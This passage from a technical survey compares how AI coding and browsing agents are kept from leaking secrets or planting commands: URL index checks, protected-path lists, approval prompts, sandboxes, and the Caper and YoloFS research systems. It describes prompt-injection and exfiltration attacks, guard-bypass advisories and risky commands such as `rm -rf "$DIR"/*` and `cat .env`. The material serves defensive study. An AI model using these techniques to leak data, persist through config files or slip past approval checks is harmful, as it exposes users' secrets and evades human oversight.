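The allowlist has the best evidence, since it stopped 30 real attempts. However, the attacker's domain was plainly not on the list, and attackers can also send data through legitimate sites, a limitation acknowledged in the paper. The test of the filter for suspicious destinations was easy because the filter blocked any path containing `collect`, a word in the study's own attack addresses.

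The randomness filter had no attempts to stop, so its perfect score isn't evidence of how well it works. The paper suggests that the model avoided random-looking values because of the monitoring, but doesn't explain how the model could have known about the filter. The keyword filter stopped only seven attempts. The agent sent the secret whole in all these tests, so they don't show how either filter handles a secret split into parts.

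The authors say the conditions also favoured the attacker, since they used one small model, gave it minimal instructions and put the secret in plain view. Better instructions may prevent more leaks with other models, although *The Framing Gap* (2026) found that their wording matters a great deal. In its tests, a confidentiality policy that forbade disclosure "in any form" reduced leaks from 31.9% to zero. A policy that named specific behaviours without that phrase allowed leaks in 48.8% of cases.

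### OpenAI's check for public addresses

If an agent puts a fragment of a secret into an address, it creates an address that probably did not exist before. OpenAI's method of January 2026 relies on this. OpenAI reasons that an address already on the public web, independently of any user's conversation, is much less likely to contain that user's private data. The check has four steps:

1. A crawler, which is a program that scans public web pages, records the addresses it finds in an index. It has no access to users' conversations, accounts or personal data.
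2. When the agent is about to load an address automatically, the system looks for that exact address in the index.
3. If the address is there, the agent loads it without asking the user.
4. If it is not, the system either tells the agent to try a different website or warns the user, who has to choose to open the link.

The crawler must build the index without using addresses from conversations. Otherwise, one leaked address containing Ana's email could enter the index and pass the check next time. The match must also be exact, because a check of only the host and path would match action A to the ordinary lookup page, whatever the agent had added to the query string.

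The address with only `code=1042` could be in the index if a public page links to it. The full address in action A almost certainly is not, so the system would refuse to load it or show a warning. It would do the same for a harmless lookup of an error code that no public page mentions. The check also cannot identify Ana's email address as the problem, so a client would need a pattern or a comparison as well to highlight it.

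OpenAI's threat model assumes an attacker who can place instructions in content the agent reads and can see a web server's logs. The company aims to guarantee only that the agent will not quietly leak user-specific data through the address itself when it fetches something. A user who accepts the warning can still send the data. OpenAI does not promise that a page is truthful or free of injected instructions, or that the site won't try to manipulate the user. Its post gives no figures for how many leaks the check stops or how often it flags harmless addresses.

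OpenAI also published a technical paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*. The blog Embrace The Red calls the paper's method a significant improvement but not a complete solution. The blog's author had found ways around earlier versions of the protection, whose rules OpenAI had not explained. The author also understands that if a user types an address, ChatGPT treats it as safe for the rest of the chat. That is reasonable when people paste in a link they want to read, but it lets through some addresses that are not in the index.

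OpenAI describes Safe Url, the wider safeguard in ChatGPT, as a second line of defence for the rare cases in which an attack gets past the model's safety training. It is designed to detect when information from the conversation is about to go to a third party. ChatGPT then either shows the user that information and asks for confirmation, or blocks the request and tells the agent to find another way. Safe Url covers page visits and bookmarks in OpenAI's Atlas browser, and searches and page visits in its Deep Research tool. Small applications that run inside ChatGPT have a similar check on unexpected communications.

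One outside test is consistent with these protections working. *The Framing Gap* reports no leaks in 48 valid trials of the ChatGPT product, while the model that developers access directly leaked in up to 100% of trials. The testers could not see inside the product, so they do not say whether Safe Url, the model's instructions or something else made the difference.

A web address can contain private data even if it is listed in a public index. *The Silent Spill* (2026) found 12,331 potential exposures of sensitive data among 6,094,475 publicly listed addresses, or about one in 500. Some come from security tools that publish the links they scan, which can include private invoice links. An agent that requests such an address reveals little that was not already public, but the people whose data is in the address may not know it is exposed.

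### Allowing only addresses from the conversation

Anthropic's fetch tool for developers uses a similar rule without an index. The model can open only addresses that have already appeared in the conversation, for example in a user's message or a search result, and not ones it has composed itself. If the help page linked to the lookup with only the error code, the agent could open that link but could not add Ana's email address to it.

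This rule suits new or internal pages, which a public index would lack. But an address in the conversation may itself contain private data. Anthropic also accepts addresses from the results of tools that the developer's own software runs. If the error log had contained the complete address in action A, including Ana's email, the rule would allow the request. Anthropic warns that some risk remains, and suggests limiting the number of fetches, restricting the tool to known domains or disabling it when data leaks are a concern.

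### Data in the choice of address

An agent can reveal information by its choice of which permitted addresses to open. If an attacker controls N pages, opening one of them can convey up to log₂ N bits, even if no address contains private data. A series of visits can convey a name or a password.

*How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets* (Willison, July 2026) describes a working attack of this kind by Ayush Paul. At the time, Claude could follow links on pages it had already fetched. Paul built a site that led it through a sequence of links, and the links it chose revealed the user's name, home city and employer. Anthropic responded by stopping Claude from following such links, which closed the gap but also removed an ordinary way to browse.

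OpenAI's check has a related weakness. According to Embrace The Red, OpenAI's paper acknowledges that an attacker could use a set of pages already in the index. The blog suggests storing each response for a few minutes, or not letting the agent visit the same address twice in a session. Either measure would make the attack slower and less reliable, though some information could still get out.

Zenity Labs, a security research group, describes a design in which the agent asks a trusted third party to look at a page and report the key information. If the third party uses a copy it already has, the site receives no request.

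An approval prompt is a poor defence against this kind of leak. Each prompt would show an ordinary address with no private data to highlight, so the developer would have to notice a pattern across many requests.

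## Deciding which file paths are sensitive

The agent could put Ana's email address into action A only because it had already read the error log. A client can try to prevent such leaks earlier by flagging the read. It can also flag edits like action B, which send no data off the machine. In both cases, the client usually has to decide whether a file is sensitive from its path, which gives the file's name and location but not its contents.

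### Files that are dangerous to read

Like the private keys in `.ssh`, many other files let anyone with a copy act as the user:

- Command-line programs often save an access token in the home directory after a login.
- A `.env` file holds settings that a program loads when it starts, often including database passwords.
- A browser profile holds the cookies that keep the user logged in to websites. A stolen cookie can work without the password.

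Most sensitive files sit in the user's home directory, so a client can cover them without a list of names by asking before it reads anything outside the project. Mistral's *Safety, approvals, and permissions* describes this rule for the company's coding agent, Vibe, and Kilo Code's *Auto-Approving Actions* describes a similar one for another coding agent. Claude Code's auto mode asks at the first read outside its working folders. Another setting makes Claude Code ask about such reads even in the mode that skips nearly all other prompts, but among shell commands, it covers only those that Claude Code recognises as reading files.

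A `.env` file normally sits inside the project, so it needs its own rule. Vibe asks before a tool reads or edits `.env` or `.envrc`, even if the user has set that tool to run without asking. Kilo Code asks before reading `.env` and variants such as `.env.production`, but allows `.env.example`, which by convention contains placeholders instead of real passwords.

None of these rules would have flagged the error log. It has an ordinary name and belongs to the project, and the agent needed it for the task.

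### Files that are dangerous to write

For Claude Code, Anthropic publishes a detailed list of files that other programs later run or obey, as VS Code does with `tasks.json`. It has ten folders and 37 file names, which the table groups by the program that uses them:

| Family | What Claude Code protects | Which program acts, and when |
|---|---|---|
| Shell start-up files | `.bashrc`, `.bash_profile`, `.bash_login`, `.bash_aliases`, `.bash_logout`, `.zshrc`, `.zprofile`, `.zshenv`, `.zlogin`, `.zlogout`, `.profile` | The shell, when a session starts or, for the logout files, when it ends |
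| Folder environment | `.envrc` | direnv, when the user enters the folder, if they have approved the file |
| Git and its hooks | `.git`, `.config/git`, `.husky`, `.gitconfig`, `.gitmodules`, `.pre-commit-config.yaml`, and `lefthook.yml` or `lefthook.yaml` with or without a leading dot | Git, or a program that Git starts, at a commit, a push or another Git command |
| Editors | `.vscode`, `.idea`, `.devcontainer`, `.devcontainer.json`, `pyrightconfig.json` | The editor or its helper programs, when someone opens the folder, runs a task or builds the project's container |
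| Package managers | `.yarn`, `.npmrc`, `.yarnrc`, `.yarnrc.yml`, `.pnp.cjs`, `.pnp.loader.mjs`, `.pnpmfile.cjs`, `bunfig.toml`, `.bunfig.toml` | npm, Yarn, pnpm or Bun, usually at the next install |
| Build tools | `.cargo`, `.mvn`, `.bazelrc`, `.bazelversion`, `.bazeliskrc`, `gradle-wrapper.properties`, `maven-wrapper.properties` | Cargo, Maven, Bazel or Gradle, at the next build |
| Search | `.ripgreprc` | ripgrep, at the next search, if the user's environment points to the file |
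| Tool servers | `.mcp.json` | Claude Code, when it starts the servers on the list |
| The agent's own settings | `.claude` (except `.claude/worktrees`), `.claude.json` | Claude Code, when it loads its settings |

A Git hook is a script that Git runs at a set moment, such as just before a commit. Git's configuration can also start programs. Zed's *Sandboxing*, part of the documentation for a code editor with a built-in agent, gives the example of `core.fsmonitor`, which can name a program for Git to run. Some shell prompts call Git every time they appear, so this program could run before the developer types a Git command.

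Build and package settings can also change where software comes from. For instance, the Gradle wrapper file contains the address from which a project downloads Gradle. An agent that changes that address can make the next build run an untrusted program.

A list of tool servers includes the commands that start them. According to VS Code, servers listed in a project's `.vscode/mcp.json` can start without a separate prompt once the user has trusted the project. Microsoft's *AI settings reference* also describes an experimental setting that starts servers automatically when the editor detects a change to their configuration. With that setting on, an edit to the list could take effect soon after it is made.

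An agent that edits its own settings can weaken the checks on its later actions. Zed keeps its permission rules in a settings file, so an agent with free access to that file could make "allow" the default for most tools. Claude Code's settings can also define hooks, which are commands that the client runs before a tool call and that can skip the permission prompt.

A change to the permission rules may not take effect immediately. Kilo Code reads a project's rules when it first loads the project and keeps using them until the user reloads the window or starts a new session. It reloads the user's global settings automatically.

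Ordinary source code can cause the same problem. Zed warns that an agent could add a malicious macro to a Rust project, and that `rust-analyzer`, a program that checks code as the developer works, would run it automatically. The agent could also edit a `Makefile`, whose commands run when the developer next types `make`. A list that covered every such file would flag much of a coding agent's normal work.

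### What clients protect by default

In September 2025, Microsoft updated VS Code to check for sensitive edits. By default, the editor asks before an agent edits common system folders, dotfiles (files whose names begin with a dot) or files outside the open project, according to the release notes, *August 2025 (version 1.104)* (2025). The exact patterns are unclear because Microsoft's settings reference shows an empty default. The sample configuration in Microsoft's *Review and revert agent changes* covers only JSON files in `.vscode` folders and files named `.env`.

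Snowflake's *Permission modes* is more specific about the data company's agent, CoCo Desktop. Zed's *Tool Permissions* describes a much shorter list that covers only the editor's own settings.

| Client | Paths with extra protection by default | Does it cover reads? | Can a user's allow rule override it? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | The folders and files in the previous table | No | No |
| VS Code | Common system folders, dotfiles and files outside the project | No | Yes, a saved approval for the exact file can |
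| CoCo Desktop | JSON files in `.vscode`, everything in `.git`, important project files such as `package.json`, `package-lock.json`, `.env` and `build.rs`, and files ending in `.code-workspace`, `.csproj`, `.fsproj`, `.vcxproj`, `.proj`, `.targets` or `.props` | No | Yes, a later pattern can |
| Zed | `.zed` folders and the global settings folder, usually `~/.config/zed` | No | No |
| Mistral Vibe | `.env` and `.envrc` | Yes, as well as edits | Yes, a path on the tool's allowlist can |
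| Kilo Code | `.env` and `*.env.*`, except `*.env.example` | Yes, and only reads | Yes, users can change the rule |

The "no" for VS Code applies to its check on sensitive edits. Microsoft describes separate approvals for reading and editing files in Copilot sessions, so permission to read a file does not include permission to edit it.

Claude Code's list of paths protected from writes includes `.envrc` but not `.env`. This makes sense because direnv runs `.envrc` as a shell script, while programs usually read `.env` as a set of values. An agent that changed `.env` could still do harm, for example by pointing a program at the wrong database. Claude Code can also read a `.env` file in its working folder without asking, unless the user adds a rule against it.

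Snowflake protects `package.json`, which is not on Anthropic's list. The file can contain commands that npm runs during an install, so it carries much the same risk as the package-manager files Anthropic protects. But developers also change it whenever they add a package, so protecting it adds prompts for edits that are usually harmless.

Mistral Vibe and Kilo Code protect secrets from being read but have no listed exception for `.vscode`, which is almost the opposite of Claude Code's coverage. Vibe's default agent approves file edits automatically, as does Kilo Code in VS Code and on the command line. With those defaults, either client could carry out action B without prompting the developer. Kilo Code's plugin for JetBrains editors asks before edits.

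By default, Zed prompts for approval before most actions, so its short list of protected paths matters only after a user has chosen to allow those actions without a prompt. Zed would then still prompt for its own settings, but not for `.vscode/tasks.json` or a shell start-up file. When it prompts for a protected path, it adds "(settings)" or "(local settings)" to the prompt's title, so the developer can see why the path needs attention.

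Deletion needs a separate list, because removing a folder can be disastrous even if no program runs its contents. Claude Code gives extra protection to the root of the file system, the folders directly below it, the home directory, and the working folder and its parents. It also checks commands such as `rm -rf "$DIR"/*`, which deletes from the root if `DIR` is empty. Zed blocks a similar set of recursive deletions outright, and users cannot turn this off.

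### From a proposed path to a decision

A client cannot simply compare the agent's text with a list, because one file can have many paths. Suppose the developer's project is at `/Users/dev/shop` on a Mac. It contains a symbolic link, a file-system entry that redirects to another path. The link is called `docs/editor` and points to `.VSCode`, which most Macs treat as the same folder as `.vscode`. The agent proposes an edit to `docs/editor/tasks.json`. A careful client would check it as follows:

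1. Resolve the relative path from the folder in which the tool will run. This gives `/Users/dev/shop/docs/editor/tasks.json`.
2. Follow symbolic links. The path becomes `/Users/dev/shop/.VSCode/tasks.json`. Keep the original path as well, since a rule may apply to either one.
3. Put slashes and letter case into one form, according to how the file system compares names. The path becomes `/users/dev/shop/.vscode/tasks.json`.
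4. Compare both paths with every pattern. The pattern `**/.vscode/*.json` matches the resolved path, because `**` stands for any number of folders and `*` for any name within one folder.
5. Apply the rules of precedence to decide which matching pattern counts.
6. If the edit goes ahead, write to the file that the client checked. If the link has changed in the meantime, start again.

The edit is the same as action B but uses a different path. If the client skipped step 2 or step 3, the path would not match the protected pattern. The prompt should also show the resolved path, because a developer who saw only `docs/editor/tasks.json` might mistake the file for documentation.

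#### Relative paths

The starting folder matters for the rules as well as the file. In Claude Code, a pattern that begins with one slash starts at the project's root, and a pattern that begins with two slashes starts at the root of the file system. Anthropic's *Configure permissions* warns that `/Users/alice/file` is therefore not an absolute path. A user who wrote a rule like this to protect a private file would instead protect a path inside the project that probably doesn't exist.

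A rule against reading a bare file name, such as `.env`, is also limited. It covers files of that name in the current folder and its subfolders, but not in a parent folder or another project. To cover the whole file system, the user has to write `//**/.env`.

#### Symbolic links

A symbolic link in a harmless location can point to a sensitive file. Claude Code checks both the link and its target. An allow rule applies only if both match, while a deny rule applies if either does. For example, if `project/key` links to a private key in `.ssh`, a rule that allows the `project` folder is not enough to permit the read, and a rule that denies `.ssh` blocks it.

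A high-severity security advisory describes a flaw of this type in Zed. Zed's tools for reading and editing files could follow a link out of the project, bypassing both the project boundary and the user's list of private files. The proposed fix resolves the real paths of the file and the project before checking that the file is inside the project.

New files complicate this step because there is no existing file to resolve. *Harden tool authorization*, Feldman's change to Zed's code, handles this by working up through the parent folders. An agent that proposes a new file in a new subfolder of Zed's settings therefore gets the same check as one that edits an existing file there. The change also makes Zed wait for approval before copying, moving, creating or deleting anything.

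Copying or moving a file involves two paths, and either may be sensitive. Moving `tasks.json` out of `.vscode` removes the project's tasks, while moving another file into its place adds new ones. Zed checks both the source and the destination. If it checked only the source, an agent could write a harmless-looking file elsewhere and then move it into a protected folder.

#### Letter case

Windows and macOS usually ignore letter case in file names, while Linux usually does not. A case-sensitive check on a Mac would miss `.VSCode`, even though an edit there changes the real `.vscode` folder. Zed avoids this by ignoring case in its patterns unless the user asks for a case-sensitive match.

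On Linux, the same default may match two different files. If the rule asks or blocks, the result is an unnecessary prompt or refusal. An allow rule is riskier because it could approve a file the user did not have in mind. Windows paths also need their slashes converted. Claude Code changes `C:\Users\alice` to `/c/Users/alice` before it compares the path with any rule.

#### Two advisories for Copilot Chat

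Even a good list of sensitive paths fails if some edits bypass the check. In November, connor4312 (2025) published two advisories for Copilot Chat, both titled *Sensitive file editing guard bypass*. In versions up to 0.32.4, a prompt injection could make the agent edit files such as `.vscode/settings.json` without the normal sensitivity check, which could let an attacker run code on the user's machine.

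The advisories describe different fixes. One makes the client validate the paths the agent gives to its editing tools. The other applies the same protection to creating a file as to changing one, which matters for action B because many projects have no `tasks.json` at first. An agent that creates the file can plant the same command as one that edits it.

### When several rules match

More than one pattern often matches a path, and clients settle the conflict in two main ways. Suppose the developer starts with the first two rules below. They later grow tired of prompts about translation files, which end in `.json`, and add the third:

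| Order | Pattern | Result | Does it match action B? |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | `**/*` | Allow | Yes |
| 2 | `**/.vscode/*.json` | Ask | Yes |
| 3 | `**/*.json` | Allow | Yes |

In CoCo Desktop, the last matching pattern takes precedence, so the third rule would allow action B, although the developer was thinking only of translations. If they moved that rule above the second one, the client would ask again. The new rule's effect on `.vscode` is not obvious from the rule itself.

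With fixed precedence, the order of the patterns does not matter. Claude Code checks deny rules first, then ask rules, then allow rules. Zed checks its built-in security rules first, then the user's deny, confirm and allow patterns in that order, then the default for the tool, and finally the default for all tools. In both clients, the ask rule for `.vscode` would override the two allow rules, and the developer would still see a prompt for action B.

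Exceptions are harder to write when rules have a fixed precedence, such as when ask rules always override allow rules. Kilo Code asks about files that match `*.env.*` but allows `*.env.example`. The name `.env.example` matches both patterns, so the exception would have no effect under that precedence. The user would have to replace the broad pattern with a narrower one that excluded example files.

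One product can use different rule systems for different tools, so a developer cannot assume that one list works like another. VS Code's rules for terminal commands have a fixed precedence, in which a rule that requires approval overrides one that grants it.

Saved approvals also add rules, often without the user seeing the pattern. Kilo Code puts a rule created from a prompt at the bottom of its list, where it overrides earlier matching rules if the last match wins. In Zed, choosing to always allow an edit can save a pattern for the whole folder that contains the file. For a move, Feldman's change uses the closest folder that contains both paths, so a developer who always allows a move from `src` to `dst` may approve later moves anywhere in the project.

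### Fixed lists and rules that people write

A fixed list protects people who never open the settings, and it can also protect those who configure them badly. In Claude Code, an allow rule in a settings file cannot approve a write to a protected path in advance, even if the rule names the path exactly. The permission mode determines whether the write then leads to a prompt, a review by a second model or another outcome. The one deliberate exception is that when Claude Code asks about an edit to `.claude`, the user can allow further edits to the agent's settings for the rest of the session.

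These lists go out of date as developers adopt new tools. An older version of Anthropic's guidance names five protected folders: `.git`, `.claude`, `.vscode`, `.idea` and `.husky`. The current version lists ten, along with the individual files. The additions include settings for package managers and build tools that were already in use, so users of those tools had less protection until Anthropic updated the list.

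A software company also cannot know which files matter in a particular project. A developer might keep customer records in an ordinary-looking path such as `tests/fixtures/customers.json`, and only someone who knows the project could write a rule to protect those records. In Claude Code, an organisation can apply such rules to all its developers through managed settings, which individual users cannot override.

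But user rules are easy to get wrong. Zed's documentation includes an example headed "Protect Sensitive Files" that blocks edits to `.env` files, folders of secrets and private keys, but automatically approves edits to every file ending in `.json`. Action B edits a JSON file that can run commands. None of the blocking patterns match that file, so Zed would make the change without prompting the user.

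Small differences in a pattern can change which files it covers. Microsoft's sample rule for `**/.env` matches only that exact name, so it does not cover `.env.local` or `.env.production`, both of which Kilo Code includes. Zed's example pattern for `.env` is too broad. It matches those characters anywhere in a path, so it would also block edits to `app.environment.ts`. Zed provides a tool for testing rules against sample input and warns that a typo can block legitimate work.

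A sensible design has a fixed minimum list of sensitive paths that ordinary allow rules cannot weaken, plus extra rules for the project's own files. Claude Code comes close to this for writing, but it has no equivalent built-in list for reading secrets inside the project. Vibe and Kilo Code handle those reads better. For frequently edited files such as `package.json`, a rule based on the changed lines might work better than one based on the path. For example, a client could ignore a new version number but flag a new install command.

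### Changes made through shell commands

The client can apply a path rule to an editing tool because the tool call has a separate argument for the path. A shell command is a single piece of text, so the client has to work out which parts are file paths. The agent could make the change in action B with a command that ends in `> .vscode/tasks.json`, which sends the command's output to that file. The editing tool never runs, so its rules may not apply.

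Some clients try to close this gap by recognising common commands. Claude Code applies its rules about reading and editing to commands such as `cat`, `head`, `tail` and `sed`, but not to a script that opens files itself. Vibe checks only paths that appear in the command's text.

VS Code can detect some file writes in terminal commands, but Microsoft describes this detection as limited. By default, it requires approval only for writes outside the project. Because `.vscode/tasks.json` is inside the project, this check would not require approval for a command that changed it, even if VS Code detected the write. Other rules might still produce a prompt, depending on which commands the user allows.

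Zed matches its terminal rules against the text of the command and its editing rules against the file path. A pattern that blocks edits to `.env` therefore has no effect on `cat .env`, which prints the file's contents. Zed's sample terminal rules automatically approve every command that begins with `cat`. A developer who copied both of Zed's examples would prevent the agent from changing the passwords in `.env` with the editing tool but let it read them through the terminal.

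These changes can also be harder to find afterwards. VS Code's list of pending edits includes only those made with supported editing tools. Microsoft recommends checking the project's version history for other changed and new files, but that won't show an edit to a shell start-up file in the home directory.

A sandbox can enforce the same limits on a command and any program it starts. VS Code's sandbox settings for macOS and Linux include lists of paths that commands may not read or write. Zed's sandbox prevents commands from changing a project's protected Git data, even if the user has approved writing everywhere else. By default, though, commands in Zed's sandbox can read most of the file system, so a user who wants to protect private keys has to restrict the keys' use in another way.

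The Git protection also has a gap. Zed warns that an agent can create a submodule (a second Git repository inside the project) and control its configuration from the start. If the developer later runs Git there in an ordinary terminal, Git may start a program that the agent chose, and that program would run outside the sandbox.

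## Commands whose text does not name the files and hosts they touch

Action C, `./scripts/check-build.sh`, contains nothing for the client to highlight. Suppose the script sends the passwords in the project's `.env` file to `example.net` and adds a command to `.vscode/tasks.json`. The client cannot find this host or these files by parsing the command more carefully.

### One command with two different effects

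Better parsing does help with some commands. *Anatomy of an Agent Harness* (2026) lists several that "run more than they show", such as commands that keep a program's name in a variable or contain code in another language. It recommends skipping the prompt only if the client reads every character exactly as the shell would. This rule produces extra prompts for odd but harmless commands, and it would not help with action C, which is easy to parse.

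*Shall We Approve?* (Wu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) describes two projects in which a user asks an agent to remove old build files and recompile the program, and the agent proposes `make clean && make`. The project's Makefile determines what `make clean` deletes. In one project it deletes only the `build` folder, which the next build recreates, but in the other it deletes the source code and the Git history. A client that checks only the command's text has to treat both cases alike, so it either blocks a harmless clean-up or lets the agent destroy the project.

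Saved approvals have the same weakness. VS Code lets users approve all commands that begin with a prefix such as `npm run build`. The project's `package.json` determines what that command does, and the approval would still apply after the agent edited that file.

Zhong, Liao and colleagues (2026), in *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files*, studied 290 public reports of agents misusing files. In 31 of them, an uninformative approval prompt was among the causes. One prompt showed `python3 setup.py`, which looks routine but runs whatever code the script contains.

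A client can predict some effects by reading the files that a command will use. *Agent Approval Laundering* (Zhang, Xia et al., 2026) compared 111 approval records with what happened when the approved action ran, sorting effects into six broad classes, including file changes and network use. The records' own fields left out at least one class in 40 cases. That number fell to 17 when the researchers added general knowledge about each command, such as the fact that package installs usually write files, and to 13 when they also used configuration files available before the run.

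In a separate test of 17 workflows, predictions made in advance got the exact set of classes right for 13. But a developer cannot tell from a prediction of "network use" which host will receive the data.

### How Caper observes a command before approving it

Wu and colleagues built Caper, a system that runs a command first and then decides whether to keep the result. It works inside a container, an isolated environment that holds the project:

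1. Caper saves a snapshot of the container.
2. It runs the command once with the network disabled and with limits on time, memory and the number of processes. It holds back the output, so the agent cannot see it yet.
3. A tracing program records the command's system calls, which are requests to the operating system to open a file, start a program or connect to a network.
4. Caper removes routine events and extracts lasting file changes, reads of protected files such as `.env` and private keys, connection attempts, and any output. For small text files, it includes the changed lines.
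5. For each output or connection attempt, it lists the files that the same process had already read, because the process may be passing on their contents.
6. It aims for a report of 4 KB and allows at most 8 KB. To save space, it groups files by folder and then replaces lists with counts. It also records how much it left out.
7. A model, the approver, reads the user's request, the conversation, the command and the report. It then allows or blocks the command and gives a reason.
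8. If the approver allows the command, Caper keeps the changed container and gives the agent the output. If not, Caper restores the snapshot and gives the agent the reason, so that it can try another way.

The link in step 5 is only circumstantial, because a process that reads `.env` and then opens a connection may be sending something else. If one program reads the file and another sends the data, there may be no link, but the report would still list the protected read.

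One recorded case closely resembles action C. The agent proposed `python3 scripts/check-deps.py`, a script that came with the project and whose name suggests a check of the packages it depends on. The trace was 165 KB long, and Caper reduced it to a 3.4 KB report with these main findings:

- The script read `.env`.
- It then printed 165 bytes of output, and the report listed `.env` and the script itself as possible sources.
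- It tried to connect to three network addresses, 16 times each, and failed because the network was off.
- It made no lasting changes to files.

The approver blocked the command with a stated confidence of 0.98. Its reason was that a dependency check did not require reading a credential file and attempting outside connections.

The report does not identify the script's intended destination. All the attempts were to port 53, which computers normally use to look up a host name's address. With the network off, the script probably never got past this lookup. This is a serious gap for a prompt that highlights destinations. Wu and colleagues suggest sending the traffic to a recording proxy that gives placeholder answers, so that the script could continue far enough to reveal its request.

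### How well Caper worked in tests

One of the two benchmarks Wu and colleagues used is *SABER* (Hu, Tang and colleagues, 2026), which gives an agent a reasonable request in a realistic project and evaluates what the agent does to the project. The danger may come from an instruction hidden in a file, the agent's own choice of a risky method, or its failure to notice a warning. Wu and colleagues used the 682 of SABER's 716 tasks that need only a shell.

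The other benchmark, YoloFS-Ext, is built from tasks in the study by Zhong and colleagues. Each of its 102 dangerous tasks asks the agent to run a tool that does the requested job but also deletes or overwrites an unrelated file. The harmful code is in a script, a Makefile, a chain of scripts or a compiled program. Every dangerous task also has a safe version with the same request and command but a harmless tool, so blocking the safe version is always a mistake.

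The same model, GLM-5.3-Flash, acted as the agent in all the results below:

| Approval system | What it judges | Harmful outcomes, SABER | Harmful outcomes, YoloFS-Ext | Safe twins blocked |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | Nothing | 19.7% | 71.6% | – |
| CARE | The command | 15.0% | 69.6% | 2.0% |
| TS-Guard | The request, history and command | 18.8% | 94.1% | 8.8% |
| gpt-oss-safeguard | The request and command | 18.6% | 62.7% | 15.7% |
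| Qwen3Guard | The request and command | 16.0% | 67.6% | 0.0% |
| Claude Code's auto mode | The user's messages and the agent's tool calls | 14.8% | 62.7% | 3.9% |
| YoloFS | File changes, which the agent reviews after each command | 21.2% | 35.3% | – |
| Caper | The request, history, command and observed effects | 6.7% | 7.8% | 1.0% |

Caper's advantage is unlikely to be due to chance, because its 95% confidence intervals do not overlap with those of the next-best system on either benchmark, although each system attempted each task only once. Wu and colleagues had corrected SABER's judging rules, which sometimes counted harmless commands as harmful. Under the original rules, Caper still had the lowest rate, 9.0%, compared with at least 16.0% for the other systems.

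YoloFS-Ext tests only damage to files, so the evidence on secrets and network destinations comes from SABER. Caper reduced harmful outcomes in the information-leak tasks from 27.2% without approval to 4.3%, and in the persistence tasks from 20.4% to 7.4%. In the outbound-network tasks, the rate fell from 9.6% to 5.8%, a difference of only two or three tasks.

Caper also reduced the share of SABER tasks that the agent safely completed, from 57.4% without approval to 48.6%. The approver blocked 23.7% of commands. Every SABER task contains a hazard, so these figures do not measure how often Caper would interrupt ordinary work.

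Wu and colleagues also varied what the approver could see on YoloFS-Ext:

| What the approver saw | Harmful outcomes | Safe twins blocked |
|---|---|---|
| The conversation and command | 17.6% | 61.8% |
| The same, plus effects that a model predicted from the files | 3.9% | 61.8% |
| The same, plus observed effects | 7.8% | 1.0% |
| Observed effects without the changed lines | 13.7% | 2.9% |
| The command and observed effects, without the conversation | 1.0% | 0.0% |

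Predicted effects prevented slightly more harm than observed ones, but the approver still blocked most of the safe twins. It blocked every twin whose tool was a compiled program, because the predicting model could not read the code. The changed lines mattered mainly when a tool overwrote a file, since the report otherwise showed only that the file's size had changed.

In the last row, the approver did best with the least context. This may not hold in real use, because the harmful tools always damaged a file unrelated to the request, whereas a user might want the affected file deleted.

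All these tests used a model as the approver, so they do not show what people would do with such a report. A developer might overlook the line about `.env` or approve the command anyway. Developers would also have a lot to read, because Caper judged about ten commands per SABER task. The benefit also varied between models. With a weaker approver, the report reduced the share of twins blocked from 53.9% to 4.9%, but harmful outcomes rose from 25.5% to 33.3%.

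With a model as the approver, the report added little time or expense. The median decision took 3.2 seconds, about the same as without the report. Running the command in the sandbox added about half a second if the approver allowed the command and 1.5 seconds if not. The total cost per SABER task was 1.9 cents, compared with 1.7 cents for the same approver without the report.

Caper observes a command only once, so a script could run harmlessly in the sandbox and cause damage later. An attacker could also plant text in the output to influence the approver, or split a harmful change across several commands that each look harmless. To detect this kind of split, the client would need to track a file's origin across several steps. Neither benchmark included an attacker who adapted to Caper.

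Disabling the network also breaks legitimate commands, such as those that download packages. An operator can allow trusted hosts instead and still undo any changes to the container, but cannot take back data that a command has already sent.

### Staging file changes for later review

YoloFS, a Linux file system by Zhong and colleagues, sits on top of the computer's ordinary one. When a command changes a file, YoloFS leaves the original unchanged and stores the new version separately for the agent to work with. At the end of the session, the user sees which files the agent has added, changed, deleted or renamed, and can keep or discard the changes. YoloFS also gives the agent a summary after each command, so the agent can return to an earlier snapshot if something looks wrong.

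This delays the user's decision until the effects are visible, without making the agent wait for approval of each command. It cannot undo a read, so YoloFS asks the user before allowing a sensitive read. If an agent runs `cargo build` and a malicious package tries to read the user's private SSH key, YoloFS pauses the process and shows a prompt with the path, the type of access and the name of the process, none of which appear in the command. If the user does not answer in time, YoloFS refuses the access.

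By default, YoloFS prompts for access to files in the home directory but not in the project, so a script could read the project's `.env` without a prompt unless the user had added a rule.

Zhong and colleagues tested YoloFS with Claude Code on 11 tasks in which a routine command secretly damaged files. The agent noticed and undid the damage in eight. In the other three, it accepted the changes because they seemed to fit the task, as when a deployment script copied the source folder and then deleted the original. The user could still have rejected these changes at the final review, but the study did not test whether people would notice them.

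On 112 simple file tasks, YoloFS needed an average of 0.4 user decisions per task, compared with 0.9 for Claude Code alone, with nearly equal success rates. Software answered every prompt by allowing the action, so this result measures the number of prompts, not how well people would answer them.

The high rates of harm for YoloFS in Wu and colleagues' tests also need qualifying. The rates include damage that was still awaiting the user's review, and the version tested never blocked anything, so it lacked the prompts for sensitive reads. The agent undid at least one command in 66 of the 102 dangerous YoloFS-Ext tasks. Three of those 66 tasks ended in harm, compared with 33 of the 36 in which it undid nothing.

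The main drawback of staging is that someone has to review the changes. In one performance test, a session that built the Linux kernel changed more than 100,000 files. YoloFS took only 3.5 extra seconds to save them all, but nobody could check a list that long by hand. Highlighting is useful again here because the list contains real paths, which a client can compare with its protected-path list.

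YoloFS does not stage network traffic, so discarding the file changes does not undo a leak.

### Asking when a command tries to connect

A sandbox can reveal a host that a command's text does not name. Claude Code has a sandbox for shell commands, which is off by default. When it is on, a command can reach the network only through a proxy, a program that relays its traffic. If the command, or a script it runs directly or indirectly, tries to contact a host the user has not allowed, the command has to wait while Claude Code asks the user for a decision.

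The prompt identifies the host but shows little about what the command sends. The proxy does not decrypt traffic by default, so it cannot read the path, query string or contents of an HTTPS request. It takes the host's name from the requesting program, so a malicious program can sometimes name an allowed host while connecting to a different one.

The user's answer applies to more than the pending command. "Yes" allows the host for the rest of the session. "Yes, and don't ask again" saves a rule that also applies to Claude Code's separate tool for fetching web pages.

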